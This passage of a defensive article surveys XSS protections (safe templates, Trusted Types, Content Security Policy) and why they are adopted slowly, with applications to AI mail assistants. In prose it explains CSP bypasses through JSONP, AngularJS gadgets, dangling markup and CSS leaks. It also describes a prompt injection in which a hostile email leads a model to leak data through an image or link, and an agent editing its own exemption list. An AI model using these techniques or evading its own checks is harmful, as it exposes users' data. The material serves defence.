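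Janc and Weichselbaum (2020), in *Towards native security defenses for the web ecosystem*, explain that an application will be free of DOM-based XSS as long as its policy creates these objects safely. That condition is demanding, because the browser would also accept a policy that returned every string unchanged and so protected nobody. Bentkowski, who had found a way past DOMPurify, similarly warned PortSwigger, a web security company, that a policy could contain a mistake or rely on a sanitiser with a known bypass. He still expected a huge benefit, partly because auditing becomes much easier.

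The browser's check also covers code that a compiler misses. Kotowicz told PortSwigger that, in Google's data, static analysis might miss over 60% of DOM-based XSS. Google first launched Trusted Types for all users on its My Google Activity history page, and within about two years had extended it to more than 130 services. Few sites outside Google have adopted it.

### Google's bug counts

Kern's earliest figures come from two large applications, each with more than 1,000 templates. One moved to strict templates in early 2013. Google's bug tracker recorded 31 XSS bugs in it in 2012, four in the year to mid-2014, and none in the last six months of that period. The other application was still migrating, and its count fell from 21 to nine. Kern calls these observations anecdotal, because bug counts also depend on things like code size and developers' understanding of security.

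The 2021 study also describes a product that had ten DOM-based XSS bugs in the year before it adopted API hardening, two in the year of adoption and one in the year after. Its team was among the first to follow the new rules strictly, so the team may have been unusually careful in other ways.

The company-wide trends are better evidence. From 2018, DOM-based XSS made up a shrinking share of the serious flaws that outsiders reported to Google. A growing proportion of those DOM-based flaws was in old code exempt from the new rules, even though the amount of exempt code was falling. Better training or testing could explain the first trend but not easily the second, since it should have helped old code as well. Part of the difference between old and new code might still exist because the old code was already worse.

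Kern (2024), in *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety*, recalls that a large application such as Gmail used to have tens of XSS vulnerabilities a year. By 2024, all the applications built on Google's hardened frameworks had a number in the low single digits between them. *An Overview of Google's Commitment to Secure by Design*, a white paper Google published that October, gives an even lower figure: an average of less than one XSS report a year in total, over three years, across hundreds of complex applications on these frameworks. The figures may differ because Kern's perhaps includes old components that still had exemptions. Nobody had found an XSS vulnerability in Google Photos, which used secure frameworks from the start.

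These are Google's own figures, and they count only the flaws that people found. The frameworks also turn on Content Security Policy, so the fall can't be attributed to templates and types alone. Still, a fall from tens of bugs in one application to about one across hundreds is too large to dismiss as a change in reporting.

Other companies may find this harder to do. Most Google developers share one code repository and one set of compilers, and all code needs review, so a small security team could impose the rules on tens of thousands of engineers. The team exempted existing code at first and cleaned it up over several years. By the end of 2020, fewer than 1% of the company's million or more JavaScript files had an exemption. During five months of the early rollout, security reviewers received fewer than eight exemption requests a week, so the safe alternatives evidently covered most of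 what developers needed.

### When the value is meant to be markup

Kern's design treats formatted text as a rare exception. Most values in a typical application are plain text or ordinary web addresses, so encoding or checking them all does no harm. In a chat window, most of the text is formatted, because replies are full of headings, tables and links.

A strict template would display such a reply as raw Markdown. To keep the formatting, the developer would have to convert the reply to HTML, sanitise it and label the result `SafeHtml`. The template engine would then not protect anything inside that HTML, so its safety would depend on the sanitiser.

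Contextual escaping can't help inside the reply because the engine infers a gap's context from the trusted text around it, and a reply contains no trusted text. Suppose one of the office worker's twelve emails has the subject `**Lisbon**`, and the model lists each sender's name in bold, using asterisks, with the subject copied beside it. The Markdown converter can't distinguish the model's asterisks from the sender's, so "Lisbon" also appears in bold. A subject containing the syntax for a link or an image could be converted in the same way.

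A developer might tell the model to escape everything it quotes. This would probably work most of the time, but a hostile email can manipulate the model, so the escaping could fail just when the worker needs it.

Other parts of Google's approach do carry over. Kern's rules treat every plain string as untrusted, so developers don't need to trace a sentence in the summary back to the emails that shaped it, which nobody can do reliably. A chat product can ban direct use of `innerHTML` and send every reply through one reviewed function that converts and sanitises it, with Trusted Types as a second check in the browser. The sanitiser could still contain a mistake, but a developer who later added a notification or a search preview couldn't accidentally display replies without sanitising them.

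The labels would need stricter definitions, because `SafeHtml` and `SafeUrl`, like `setHTML`, protect only against scripts. The address of the stranger's image would be a valid `SafeUrl`. Google's checker even permits plain strings as image addresses, because no modern browser runs code from them. That was reasonable for XSS, but it would not protect the mailbox.

`TrustedResourceUrl` is a better pattern for images because it depends on whether the resource is trustworthy. An assistant could refuse every image address the model writes. If the worker wanted to see a picture from an email, the model could supply the attachment's number. The program could then check that the worker has access to the attachment and build the address itself.

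For some tasks, the developer can write all the markup instead of leaving it to the model. A mail summary has a predictable shape, so the developer could write a template with gaps for the sender, the subject and a one-sentence summary. The program would copy the sender and subject from the email, and the model would write only the sentence. Every gap would then hold plain text, and a strict template would work as Kern intended. Some newer interface formats go further and restrict a model to a fixed set of components. But a summary template can't display the comparison table that the worker asks for next, and people use chat assistants largely because they can ask for things no developer planned.

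Google's rules also apply, almost unchanged, to program code that models write. Samuel, Palmer and colleagues argue that models repeat the insecure patterns in their training data and are unreliable at finding their own mistakes. A compiler error that gives the exact position of a problem would give a model more reliable information. They propose building contextual escaping into programming languages, so that a model or a person could make a piece of HTML safe by adding a short tag in front of it. They have a working prototype but report no experiments with code-writing models.

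The exemptions may be the weak point. Google relies on human reviewers to notice code that evades its checks, which becomes harder as models write more of the code. An agent trying to make a failing program compile might disguise a sink or add its own file to the exemption list, so the list would have to be stored where the agent can't edit it.

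## Content Security Policy and the failure of domain allowlists

Google's hardened frameworks still let through an occasional XSS bug, and most sites have nothing as thorough. Content Security Policy (CSP) is a second barrier for when encoding or sanitising fails. A site sends the browser a list of rules with each page, and the browser enforces them even if an attacker has injected markup. At first these rules mostly named trusted domains, which gave very little protection against XSS. A later approach, which marks individual scripts, does much better. Neither approach reliably stops data from leaving the page, which is the greater danger for a mail assistant.

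### The 2010 design

In *Reining in the Web with Content Security Policy* (2010), Stamm, Sterne and Markham of Mozilla argued that validating input is important but never perfect. They wanted sites to name the servers they trust and browsers to refuse content from any others.

A browser can't tell the server's own scripts from injected ones, so Stamm and colleagues banned inline scripts, which are written directly into the page. A site that used CSP had to move its scripts into separate files, and the browser would run only files from origins on the site's list. The browser also refused to turn strings into code while a script was running, because an attacker might control part of the string.

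In the syntax that browsers use today, the mail site might send this policy:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self';
  script-src 'self' https://static.example.com;
  img-src 'self';
  object-src 'none'
```

Each directive names a kind of resource and then the permitted sources.

- `default-src 'self'` limits the page to resources from its own origin, unless another directive covers that kind of resource.
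- `script-src` permits scripts from the page's own origin and from `static.example.com`. It replaces the default instead of adding to it, so the developer has to repeat `'self'`.
- `img-src 'self'` permits images only from the page's own origin. The default would have done the same here.
- `object-src 'none'` bans plug-ins such as Flash, which could run scripts in the page.

If an attacker's markup gets into the page anyway, the browser won't run any inline scripts, event handlers or JavaScript links in it, because the policy restricts scripts and makes no exception for inline ones. The browser also won't request a script from the attacker's server, because that server doesn't match `script-src`. It blocks images from the server under `img-src` in the same way, so the attacker can't use an image's address to send data out. Stamm and colleagues tried an inline script and an outside image on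 a copy of Mozilla's add-ons site, and their modified Firefox blocked both.

The browser can also report violations to the site. The designers expected these reports to help even if few visitors had a browser that supported CSP, since one report can reveal a flaw that affects everyone. But W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft from the web's main standards consortium, warns that attackers control part of the reports' content. A report can include the first 40 characters of a blocked script, so a dashboard that displays reports must encode them like any other untrusted text.

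According to Stamm and colleagues, to run a script on a protected page, an attacker would have to inject a script element, point it to an allowed origin, and control the contents of the script there. The last condition turned out to be easy to meet on many of the domains that sites commonly trusted.

### Google's study of 26,011 policies

In *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (2016), Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues used Google's search index to test the policies that sites had deployed. The index held about 100 billion pages from over a billion hostnames, all crawled within about 20 days. They found policies on 1,680,867 hosts, but about a million of these belonged to five e-commerce platforms that used only a few policies between them. They therefore counted each distinct policy once, which left 26,011.

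They didn't attack any sites. They assumed that an attacker had already found a way to inject markup, since that is the situation CSP exists for, and asked whether the policy would then stop a script. Their program judged a policy bypassable if it had at least one of four faults:

1. It allowed inline scripts without requiring a nonce, a random value that marks the scripts the server intended.
2. It restricted scripts but not plug-ins.
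3. It allowed scripts or plug-ins from any host, or from any address with a scheme such as `https:`.
4. It allowed a domain where the researchers had found a way to run an attacker's code.

To find such domains, they searched the index for two common patterns. The first was an endpoint that copies part of the request's address into the start of a script. They tested each candidate by changing that part of the address and checking whether the change appeared in the response, and found such endpoints on 194,908 domains. The second was a copy of AngularJS, a popular Google library, which 101,330 domains hosted.

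| | All distinct policies | Enforced policies that restrict scripts | Those without inline scripts or catch-all sources |
|---|---|---|---|
| Number of policies | 26,011 | 22,425 | 2,437 |
| Allowed inline scripts | 84.38% | 87.63% | 0% |
| Left plug-ins unrestricted | 12.04% | 9.40% | 14.28% |
| Allowed any host | 22.12% | 21.48% | 0% |
| Allowed an unsafe domain | 75.81% | 79.17% | 41.65% |
| Bypassable in at least one way | 94.72% | 94.68% | 51.05% |

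The best-known result, 94.72%, is mainly due to inline scripts rather than domain allowlists. Most of the policies allowed inline scripts, usually because the site's own pages still depended on them, and such a policy fails however good its list of domains is. Many of the 75.81% of policies with an unsafe domain also allowed inline scripts. The shares of policies with each fault imply that at least 60% of all policies had both.

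The last column is a fairer test of the allowlists because its 2,437 policies came from developers who had avoided the obvious mistakes. Of these policies, 41.65% still allowed a domain that an attacker could use. The true share was probably higher, because the researchers searched automatically for only a few kinds of bypass and many others are specific to one application.

Longer allowlists were easier to bypass. Very short lists often held up, but the researchers could bypass 94.8% of the policies that allowed 12 hosts, which was the median number. The longest list allowed 512. Cleaning up the worst domains would not have helped much. Attackers could bypass 68% of all policies using only the ten most useful domains, but if the owners of those ten had removed the unsafe endpoints and libraries, attackers could still have bypassed 66% through other domains on the lists.

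### How a trusted domain runs an attacker's code

CSP's designers assumed that a trusted domain would serve only safe scripts. But a domain can host thousands of files and services, and an attacker needs only one that can be used to run malicious code.

Most of the unsafe endpoints used JSONP, a way of sharing data between sites. The same-origin policy lets a page run another site's scripts but generally not read its data, so a JSONP service sends its data as a script that passes the data to a function. The requesting page names the function in the request URL. If the service doesn't check the name, an attacker can put code there instead. The service copies the code into its response, and the browser runs it as a script from an allowed domain.

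In 39% of the JSONP bypasses, an attacker could run any code. In the others, the service accepted only a function's name, so the attacker could call only functions already in the page. Weichselbaum and colleagues considered these bypasses equally harmful in practice. That may be too pessimistic for a simple page, but a mail site probably has functions that send and delete mail.

AngularJS caused a different problem because it looks for templates in the page and evaluates the expressions in them. An attacker could inject a script element that loaded AngularJS from an allowed domain, followed by a template. The template contained no script, so CSP didn't apply to it, and the library ran the attacker's expression. CSP's ban on turning strings into code didn't help, because AngularJS had a special mode for sites with CSP in which it interpreted the expressions itself. The attack worked even if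 the site didn't use AngularJS, as long as one of its allowed domains hosted a copy.

Browsers are also lenient about what counts as a script. An error message that repeats part of the request, a spreadsheet export or a user-uploaded file may run as JavaScript if its text is valid code. This is not a flaw in the domain that serves the text, so the domain's owners had no reason to change anything, and they often could not know which sites had allowlisted them.

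The second version of CSP let developers allow a single path instead of a whole domain. But browsers ignore the path after a redirect, because otherwise a malicious site could use its own policy to discover where other sites redirect their visitors. If any allowed domain redirects to an address the attacker supplies, the attacker can load any file from a domain where the developer allowed only one path.

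In February 2015, Google introduced a CSP allowlist for Google Maps Activities, an application with four million monthly users. The team made five major changes to the policy that year to keep up with changes in the code and the servers. After these changes, the list had 15 long paths, at least one of which led to a JSONP endpoint, so even a policy written by security specialists gave little protection against XSS.

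### Nonces and `strict-dynamic`

Weichselbaum and colleagues proposed that developers stop listing domains and mark each script with a nonce instead. CSP already supported this, but fewer than 1% of the policies used it. The server generates a new random value for every response and puts it both in the policy and on each script element it intends to send:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'nonce-k7Qx2mVd' 'strict-dynamic';
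  base-uri 'none'

<script nonce="k7Qx2mVd" src="/mail.js"></script>
```

Under a nonce-based policy, an attacker can still inject a script element but can't guess the nonce, so the browser doesn't run the script. A JSONP endpoint on a trusted domain no longer lets the attacker bypass the policy. W3C recommends nonces of at least 128 bits.

Nonces alone would break many pages, because third-party libraries often load further scripts without attaching the page's nonce. The researchers therefore proposed `strict-dynamic`, a keyword that lets a script with a valid nonce create further script elements, which the browser runs whatever domain they load from. The browser still blocks script elements that the parser finds in markup without a valid nonce, and an attacker's script would normally arrive that way. It also ignores any domains the policy lists for scripts.

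The last directive, `base-uri`, prevents an attack that nonces alone don't stop. An HTML page can contain a `base` element, which changes the server that relative URLs such as `/mail.js` refer to. Without the directive, an attacker could inject a `base` element and make a script with a valid nonce load from the attacker's server.

Google Maps Activities already had nonces on its scripts, so it switched to a policy of nonces with `strict-dynamic` without rewriting any code. By the time of the study, it had not needed to change the policy again. The researchers analysed hundreds of XSS bugs inside Google and, on that basis, expected such policies to stop a large majority of attacks. They were assessing their own proposal, but W3C's draft now calls the same combination "Strict CSP" and describes it as effective and practical to deploy. However, the draft also says that developers should avoid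 `strict-dynamic` when possible, and its opening example is still a domain allowlist.

An attacker can sometimes use a page's nonce without knowing its value, for example by injecting an unfinished script element just before a genuine one. The parser then reads the genuine element's nonce as part of the attacker's element. Browsers check for signs of this, but W3C notes that one variant escapes the check because the parser discards duplicate attributes before the check can examine them.

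In a chat window, a strict policy would have limited the damage from the mistake in Auth0's tutorial. A nonce can't authorise an inline event handler, so the browser would have blocked any in the model's reply.

### Script gadgets

Nonces rely on the developer's scripts doing only what the developer intended. In May 2017 Sebastian Lekies, who co-wrote the study, presented ways to bypass CSP using code from common web frameworks. They rely on script gadgets, which are pieces of legitimate code in the page that turn harmless-looking markup into running script.

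The 2016 study had already included a small example, in which a script reads a text field, treats the first word as a function name and calls that function with the rest. The developer expects the script to read the page's own text field, but an attacker who can inject markup can supply another. The script has a valid nonce and the text field doesn't need one, so the attacker chooses what runs without injecting a script. AngularJS works as a gadget in the same way on any site that deliberately loads it, because the attacker only has to inject a template.

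Some gadgets are more dangerous with `strict-dynamic` than with a domain allowlist. If a trusted script creates a script element using an address from the page, a browser with an allowlist would check the domain, but with `strict-dynamic` it loads the file from anywhere. W3C advises developers to audit every place where their code does this, which is difficult when much of the code comes from frameworks. Trusted Types would catch a gadget that passes a plain string to a dangerous sink, but not one that only calls one of the page's own functions.

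A chat product's own scripts may act on attributes that the browser ignores, for instance by turning any element with a certain label into a button that performs an action. A sanitiser that removes only scripts and event handlers from replies would leave those attributes in place. Allowing only the few attributes that formatted text needs would be safer.

### Stealing data without a script

An attacker could still steal data from a page even if the browser blocked every injected script. The security researcher Michał Zalewski described several ways to do this in 2011. One is to inject an image tag with an opening quotation mark before the address and no closing one. The browser then reads everything up to the next quotation mark on the page as part of the address and sends it to the attacker's server. Another is to change the destination of a form already on the page, so that whatever the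 user types into it goes to the attacker.

In 2012 Mario Heiderich and others combined style sheets and vector graphics to similar effect. W3C's draft describes one such technique. A style rule applies only if a hidden value begins with a certain letter, and it then loads a background image specific to that letter. The attacker learns the letter from the image the browser requests, and can work out the rest in the same way. Browsers now hide nonces from style sheets for this reason.

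CSP can block many of these attacks, because most of them end in a request to the attacker's server. But the people who worked on CSP disagreed about whether it was meant to. Stamm and colleagues had promised that information would go only to servers the site had authorised. *Data Exfiltration in the Face of CSP*, by Van Acker, Hausknecht and Sabelfeld, collects later statements from researchers and from W3C's mailing list. Barth wrote in 2012, "We're never going to plug all the exfiltration vectors," and didn't think it was worth trying. Mike West, an editor of the specification, preferred not to give up on the idea entirely. Meanwhile, other researchers had built security tools that relied on CSP to stop leaks, as had Van Acker in earlier work.

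Van Acker and colleagues then tested the assumption. They wrote pages with a policy that allowed the page's own scripts and nothing else, and tried to get data out through features that browsers use to save time. For example, a browser may look up a linked site's numerical address before anyone clicks the link. An attacker who runs the name server that receives the lookup can read stolen data placed in front of the site's name. Browsers may also fetch a whole page in advance if the markup suggests that the user will need it.

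All twelve browsers tested leaked data, one of them only under certain conditions. Only nine supported CSP, so the results from the other three aren't evidence of how well it works. These browser versions date from 2015, and W3C has since brought prefetching pages under `default-src`. Prefetching is still uncontrolled if a policy has no `default-src`, and CSP still doesn't cover the name lookups.

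### Which ways out a policy closes

The W3C's CSP draft now has a short section on exfiltration. According to that section, CSP can mitigate leaks if a site lists the servers its page may contact, but the protection is only as strong as the weakest list in the policy. A policy that blocks everything except images, but allows images from any server, does not prevent leaks through image requests.

| How data might leave | What controls it |
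|---|---|
| The address of an image | `img-src` |
| A request or lasting connection opened by a script | `connect-src` |
| The address of a font, style sheet, video or frame | A directive for each, or `default-src` |
| A form sent to another site | `form-action`, which `default-src` does not replace |
| A page fetched in advance | `default-src`, together with the policy's other lists |
| A name lookup in advance | Nothing in CSP |
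| A link that the user clicks | Nothing in CSP |
| A script that sends the tab to another site or opens a new window | Nothing in CSP |

For the mail assistant, `img-src 'self'` would have blocked the image the stranger asked for, no matter how the model wrote it. The `connect-src` directive matters mainly if a script is already running, so it adds little protection against a reply that contains only text and pictures.

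But people want to see the pictures in their mail. If the site allowed images from anywhere, it would reopen the leak. It could instead fetch pictures through its own server, but a server that requested any address it received would itself pass the reference number to the stranger.

An allowed server can also leak data because many customers share it. HUMAN Security demonstrated this against Twitter with Google Analytics, a service that counts visits to websites. Its researchers sent a username and password to their own Analytics account, in the field for the name of the page visited. Twitter's policy had to allow the Analytics server, and it could not allow Twitter's account while blocking the researchers'. Data later leaked out of AI products through allowed domains too.

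Links are the largest gap in CSP for an assistant. The stranger could ask for a link instead of an image, put the reference number in the link's address, and label it "View the full summary". Stamm and colleagues deliberately left clicked links out of CSP because they considered tricking users a separate problem. That was reasonable for a site where an attacker first had to find an XSS flaw. With a mail assistant, the attacker only has to send an email, and the link appears in the product's own answer, where the worker has little reason to distrust it.

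### The removal of `navigate-to`

W3C's working group tried to close this gap. In 2016 Artur Janc, a Google security engineer, wrote that an attacker who could navigate the page or open a new window needed no other technique, because "it will always work". Van Kesteren (2016), who edits several web standards, replied that the group should work out a plan. The plan became `navigate-to`, a directive that would have listed where a page could send its user through a link, form or script. In a 2018 thread, a participant suggested it as the answer to all the leaks under discussion.

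The group removed `navigate-to` from the draft in September 2022. According to CentralCSP's vendor documentation page *navigate-to*, the members never settled how the directive should handle redirects and navigation between origins, and no browser ever shipped it to users. A developer commented in WebKit Bugzilla (2022), the bug tracker for Safari's engine, that it had little support outside Chrome and that Chrome's developers also wanted it removed. W3C's draft of August 2026 contains no replacement.

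West's later proposal, *Connection Allowlists*, is a header separate from CSP, with a single list of permitted destinations for all of a page's connections, including name lookups. West argues that CSP's division into images, fonts and scripts is the wrong way to prevent leaks, because a leak through a font request is as bad as one through an image request. The browser would apply the list in its general fetching procedure, which should also cover navigation.

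Chrome 152 introduces Connection Allowlists, according to Chrome for Developers' *FedCM* (2026), after a trial scheduled for versions 148 to 151 (Chrome for Developers, *Connection Allowlists origin trial*). Other browsers may not follow. The proposal isn't on W3C's standards track, and West (2026) reported in February that neither Apple nor Mozilla had formally responded.

The header also applies to only one page, not to a whole origin, so an attacker who can run scripts might act through another page of the same site that has a looser list. West suggests putting the restricted page in a sandbox that separates it from its origin. The draft blocks every redirect for now, which West expects to be too strict for real sites. The header's patterns can be more precise than CSP's, so a developer might be able to permit only one account on an analytics server if the account's number appears in the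 address. Otherwise, the leak that HUMAN Security demonstrated would still work.

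## Why most sites never finished deploying Content Security Policy

Since 2016, a site has been able to stop most XSS attacks with a Content Security Policy that uses nonces and `strict-dynamic`. Ten years later, about a fifth of popular sites send some kind of policy, but very few send this kind. Many developers started with a weak policy and never tightened it, or tested a policy and never enforced it.

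### Early adopters

In 2014, Michael Weissbacher, Tobias Lauinger and William Robertson of Northeastern University published a study of CSP on the million most popular websites. Threatpost reported that they followed the sites for 16 months and found it difficult to deploy CSP properly without breaking a site. Only 1% of the top 100 sites enforced a policy. In a summary of the study for a W3C mailing list, Oda noted that many of the sites using CSP did so only because their software, such as the database tool phpMyAdmin or the file-sharing program ownCloud, came with a policy.

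The researchers also tried to write policies themselves, using report-only mode, in which the browser reports what a policy would have blocked but doesn't block it. Browser extensions caused many of the reports because they add their own code to the pages a visitor opens. Neither an automatic crawl nor browsing by hand found everything a policy had to allow, so a person still had to do part of the work. Advertising was a particular obstacle because an advertising network can load scripts from domains the site's developer has never heard of. The researchers recommended moving advertisements into sandboxed frames instead of listing every possible network.

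### Ten thousand sites from 2012 to 2018

*Complex Security Policy?* (Roth, Barron and colleagues, 2020) used the Internet Archive to reconstruct seven years of policies from 10,000 popular sites. Only eight of the sites used CSP before 2014. By December 2018, 1,032 enforced a policy, but only 421 of those policies restricted scripts. The others mostly made browsers use encrypted connections or stopped other sites from showing the page in a frame. A developer can do either with one line, usually without rewriting the page.

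Almost 90% of the policies that restricted scripts contained `unsafe-inline`, a keyword that allows inline scripts, without a nonce or similar marker to cancel it. Only 40 sites had a script policy that avoided both this keyword and catch-all sources such as `https:`. Sixteen of them were adult sites with identical lists of domains. Their operators had tried the policy on one site before extending it to the others. The researchers didn't check the 40 policies for unsafe endpoints on allowed domains, so attackers may have been able to bypass some of them too.

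Airbnb's policy shows how much work an allowlist could take. In November 2014 the company started with a report-only policy that allowed scripts from 17 listed sites. The list had grown to 21 sites by March 2015, when Airbnb replaced it with a rule that allowed scripts from any HTTPS address. It enforced a policy on 1 May, switched CSP off eight days later and switched it on again on 22 May. Over the next two and a half years, Airbnb changed the policy 222 times but still allowed scripts from any HTTPS address. In January 2018 it enforced a limited list, but gave up after three days. It succeeded in March with a list of 33 sites, but then had to update the policy almost daily to match changes in its own inline scripts.

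Other sites gave up on CSP. Roth and colleagues found 294 that had used it, either enforced or report-only, but no longer did in the last month of the study. Of these, 79 had used it for at least a year. To find out why sites gave up, the researchers took 63 that had stopped restricting content and loaded archived copies of their pages in Chrome. On 15 sites, the last policy had blocked something the page used, and on nine of those the blocked code came from a third party. Another 25 had growing lists of outside domains, so the researchers guessed that maintaining the policy had become too much work.

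Of the 449 sites that tried a Content Security Policy in report-only mode, more than half never enforced any policy afterwards, and only 130 went on to enforce one that restricted content. Report-only mode was still useful, because it let developers discover that a policy would break their pages before it affected any visitors.

### Expired and mistyped domains

An allowlist assumes that a domain name will always lead to the server the developer had in mind. Roth and colleagues tested this on the 373 sites whose script policies listed at least one domain. They found that 50 of them, or 13%, had trusted a domain that an attacker could have abused:

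- Fifteen sites listed a domain that had expired or that nobody had registered, so anyone could have bought it and served scripts from it.
- Eleven sites listed what appeared to be a misspelt name. One such name stayed in the policy of Experian, a credit-reporting company, for seven months.
- Twenty-six sites, including Dropbox, listed a domain that pointed to an address on a private network. An attacker on the same network as a visitor, for instance in a café, could have served a script from that address.

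Two sites must have had more than one of these faults, since the three figures add up to 52. The practical risk was probably small for most of the 50, because their policies also allowed inline scripts, so an attacker didn't need to buy a domain. The problem is more serious for the few sites with careful policies. A listed domain can expire while the policy stays the same, so developers have to keep checking even a correct allowlist.

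### Adoption in 2025 and 2026

The most recent figures come from *10 years of watching the web*, published by Scott Helme's company, Report URI. Helme has crawled the top million sites every day since 2016. On 13 June 2026, 819,002 sites responded and 170,057 of them sent a policy, up from about 1,400 in 2016. Report URI sells CSP monitoring, so it benefits if site owners think their policies need attention. But it publishes the raw data, and *Security*, a chapter of HTTP Archive's 2025 Web Almanac, found similar adoption in a separate crawl, where the share of sites with CSP rose from 18.5% to 21.9% in a year.

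| | Roth and colleagues, 2018 | HTTP Archive, 2025 | Report URI, 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sites with a policy | 10.3% | 21.9% | 20.8% |
| Percentages below refer to | Policies that restrict scripts | Policies with a `script-src` directive | All policies |
| Contain `unsafe-inline` | Almost 90%, not counting policies with nonces | 92% | 46.8% |
| Contain a nonce | 5% | About 20% | 24.7% |
| Contain `strict-dynamic` | Under 2% | About 10% | 1.6% |

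The two recent figures for `unsafe-inline` differ mainly because Report URI counts all policies, including those that only control encryption or framing. Those policies don't need the keyword, but they don't block scripts either, so the 53.2% of policies without it don't all protect against XSS. HTTP Archive's 92% overstates the problem, because browsers ignore `unsafe-inline` when the policy also has a nonce, and some developers keep it only for old browsers. About 20% of the policies in HTTP Archive's count had nonces, so at most about 80% actually allowed inline scripts, a modest improvement on 2018.

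The spread of nonces is the clearest progress in these figures, although the samples differ. But a nonce gives little protection if the policy also allows scripts from an unsafe domain or if the server reuses the nonce. Counting policies with nonces doesn't show how many sites make these mistakes.

Trusted Types, which Google uses against DOM-based XSS, has hardly spread. In Helme's crawl, only 318 sites required it, or 0.2% of those with a policy. HTTP Archive found one Trusted Types policy in about 12% of the mobile headers it collected, but couldn't explain why. The policy sends its reports to an address containing "Android", so a single service may be responsible for all of those headers.

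### What stopped developers

In *12 Angry Developers* (2021), Roth, Gröber and colleagues studied why policies stayed weak by interviewing 12 developers who had worked with CSP. They then asked the developers to write a policy for a small note-taking application, built to include inline scripts, event handlers and third-party libraries.

Inline code was the most common problem in the application itself. Nonces don't work on inline event handlers, as one participant discovered, so developers have to move each handler on every page into a script. The earlier archive study suggests that this obstacle was common, since 68% of the 467 sites that never managed to remove insecure keywords from their policies had event handlers on their start page.

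Third-party code and frameworks were harder to handle because the developers couldn't change them. Four participants said advertisements or outside libraries forced them to loosen their policies, and six mentioned frameworks or plug-ins that didn't work with CSP. In the coding task, ten of the 12 allowed a third party's entire domain. None put a nonce on the third-party scripts, which would have been the easiest and safest solution. Many had followed guides or policy generators that recommended listing domains, and one widely read guide presented nonces only as a way to permit inline scripts.

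Ten participants mentioned cost, and half admitted that companies often treat security as secondary when building an application. They also worried about breaking their sites. One said that it was "very easy to break your site with CSP", for example by forgetting a payment service that loads on only one page. A mistake like that loses sales immediately, whereas `unsafe-inline` does no visible harm until somebody finds an XSS flaw, so it is understandable that developers left the keyword in.

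Report URI agrees that keeping `unsafe-inline` is rational for a developer who doesn't know which inline scripts the site uses. It recommends running the policy in report-only mode and collecting reports from real visitors. The interviews suggest that interpreting these reports is harder than collecting them. Four participants described getting so many reports that it took great effort to separate the genuine ones from the false ones. One described a team whose faulty policy produced hundreds of errors per page and overwhelmed its own reporting server.

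Twelve interviews can identify reasons but can't show how common each one is, and these didn't include developers who had never tried CSP. But a small survey in the archive study is consistent with them. Of 31 site operators who already knew about CSP, 29 thought it could help protect their site against XSS, but only two said their site would work with a reasonably secure policy straight away.

### Defaults and upkeep

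The protections that spread fastest over the decade were the ones providers could switch on for their customers. Cloudflare, which delivers pages for many websites, turned on a form of error reporting by default. The number of sites with the header for it rose from about 12,000 in 2020 to 289,021 in 2026, and about 97% of them send their reports to Cloudflare. After Cloudflare and Google enabled encryption designed to resist quantum computers, 44% of responding sites came to support it. The number of sites with Extended Validation certificates, which somebody has to choose, buy and renew, fell by 51%.

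CSP has also spread through platforms. HTTP Archive found a policy on 99.99% of LiveJournal's blogs and about 96% of the sites made with GoDaddy's website builder. A provider can turn on encryption for every customer because encryption works whatever the page contains, but it can't do the same with a strict script policy, which has to account for every script on the page. A policy that suits every customer is usually weak, and the most common policies in the Web Almanac mostly just upgrade connections or control framing.

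Progress in strengthening CSP policies is more fairly described as slow than stalled, because nonces seem to have become more common since 2018. Report URI lists policy strength among the things that "stalled without active ownership", but its figures on strength come from a single day, so they can't show a trend.

A default can also fail if it gets in a developer's way. Roth and colleagues describe an experiment that tested how a framework enforcing CSP by default affected 30 students as they built a page with an embedded Google map. The results suggested that this default didn't improve security. The map came from another site, so the students had to deal with the policy before their page would work, and someone in that position may loosen the policy until the page works.

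*CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (Zorz, 2026) reports that CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, also wants software makers to remove recurring weaknesses at the source instead of leaving defenders to deal with them. But CSP, as most sites use it, requires every site's developers to work out their own policy.

### Google's central rollout

Google had the same kinds of old code as everyone else, but it didn't leave the work to each product's developers. Weichselbaum (2024), in *Google's Recipe for Scaling (Web) Security*, explains that filing hundreds of bugs asking developers to deploy CSP would probably produce policies that attackers could bypass. Google's security engineers therefore made most of the changes themselves, in five steps:

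1. They used traffic logs to build an inventory of Google's web applications and ranked them by how much harm an attack could do.
2. They collected violation reports from browsers and ran checks on the source code to find what a strict policy would break.
3. They fixed the most common problems across many applications at once. An internal tool sent out hundreds of code changes for review and ran the automated tests.
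4. They enforced the policy for a gradually increasing share of traffic, so that they could quickly reverse it if something broke.
5. They kept monitoring traffic and checking new code, so that no application could quietly lose its protection.

The second step uses the same browser reports that overwhelmed some of the interviewed developers. Google could make better use of the reports because one team examined many applications together, and a fix for a common problem helped all those applications. For Trusted Types, Weichselbaum also recommends collecting reports from only a fraction of traffic, which should keep their number manageable.

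By July 2024, Google was enforcing a strict CSP on more than 900 applications, including internal ones, and Trusted Types on about 600. The strict CSP covered over 90% of its most sensitive applications, in which an attack could take over a user's account. In 2023 alone, 166 services began to enforce a strict CSP and 176 began to enforce Trusted Types, while engineers removed 438 dangerous assignments from old code. New applications built on Google's hardened frameworks have both protections from the start and don't need a separate security review before launch.

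Weichselbaum does not say how much money or staff time the rollout took. Both must have been considerable, since the rollout relied on a specialist team, a company-wide system for analysing traffic and tools for changing hundreds of applications at once. But each of the 900 applications probably took much less of both than if 900 teams had learned CSP separately. A company with a single website would have to pay for much of the same expertise and could use it on only one site.

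Outside Google, XSS remains extremely common, and it still tops MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025). The ranking draws on 39,080 recorded vulnerabilities, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses of 2025 Revealed* (2025). XSS probably ranks first more because the flaws are numerous than because attackers exploit them often. MITRE lists only seven XSS vulnerabilities that attackers are known to have exploited, compared with 20 for flaws that let an attacker run operating-system commands. The ranking shows that developers still introduce XSS flaws, but it can't measure how well CSP works, because a policy limits what an attacker can do with a flaw without removing it.

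### Defaults for model interfaces

A few companies, such as OpenAI, Google, Microsoft and Anthropic, run the assistants that most people use. Each controls the page or application that displays its model's replies, so it can protect all its users with one change, much as Cloudflare did for its customers. Google has already done this for scripts. Weichselbaum names Gemini among the applications whose framework provides a strict CSP and Trusted Types. Ordinary XSS should therefore become rare in the largest chat products, even if their models often write hostile markup.

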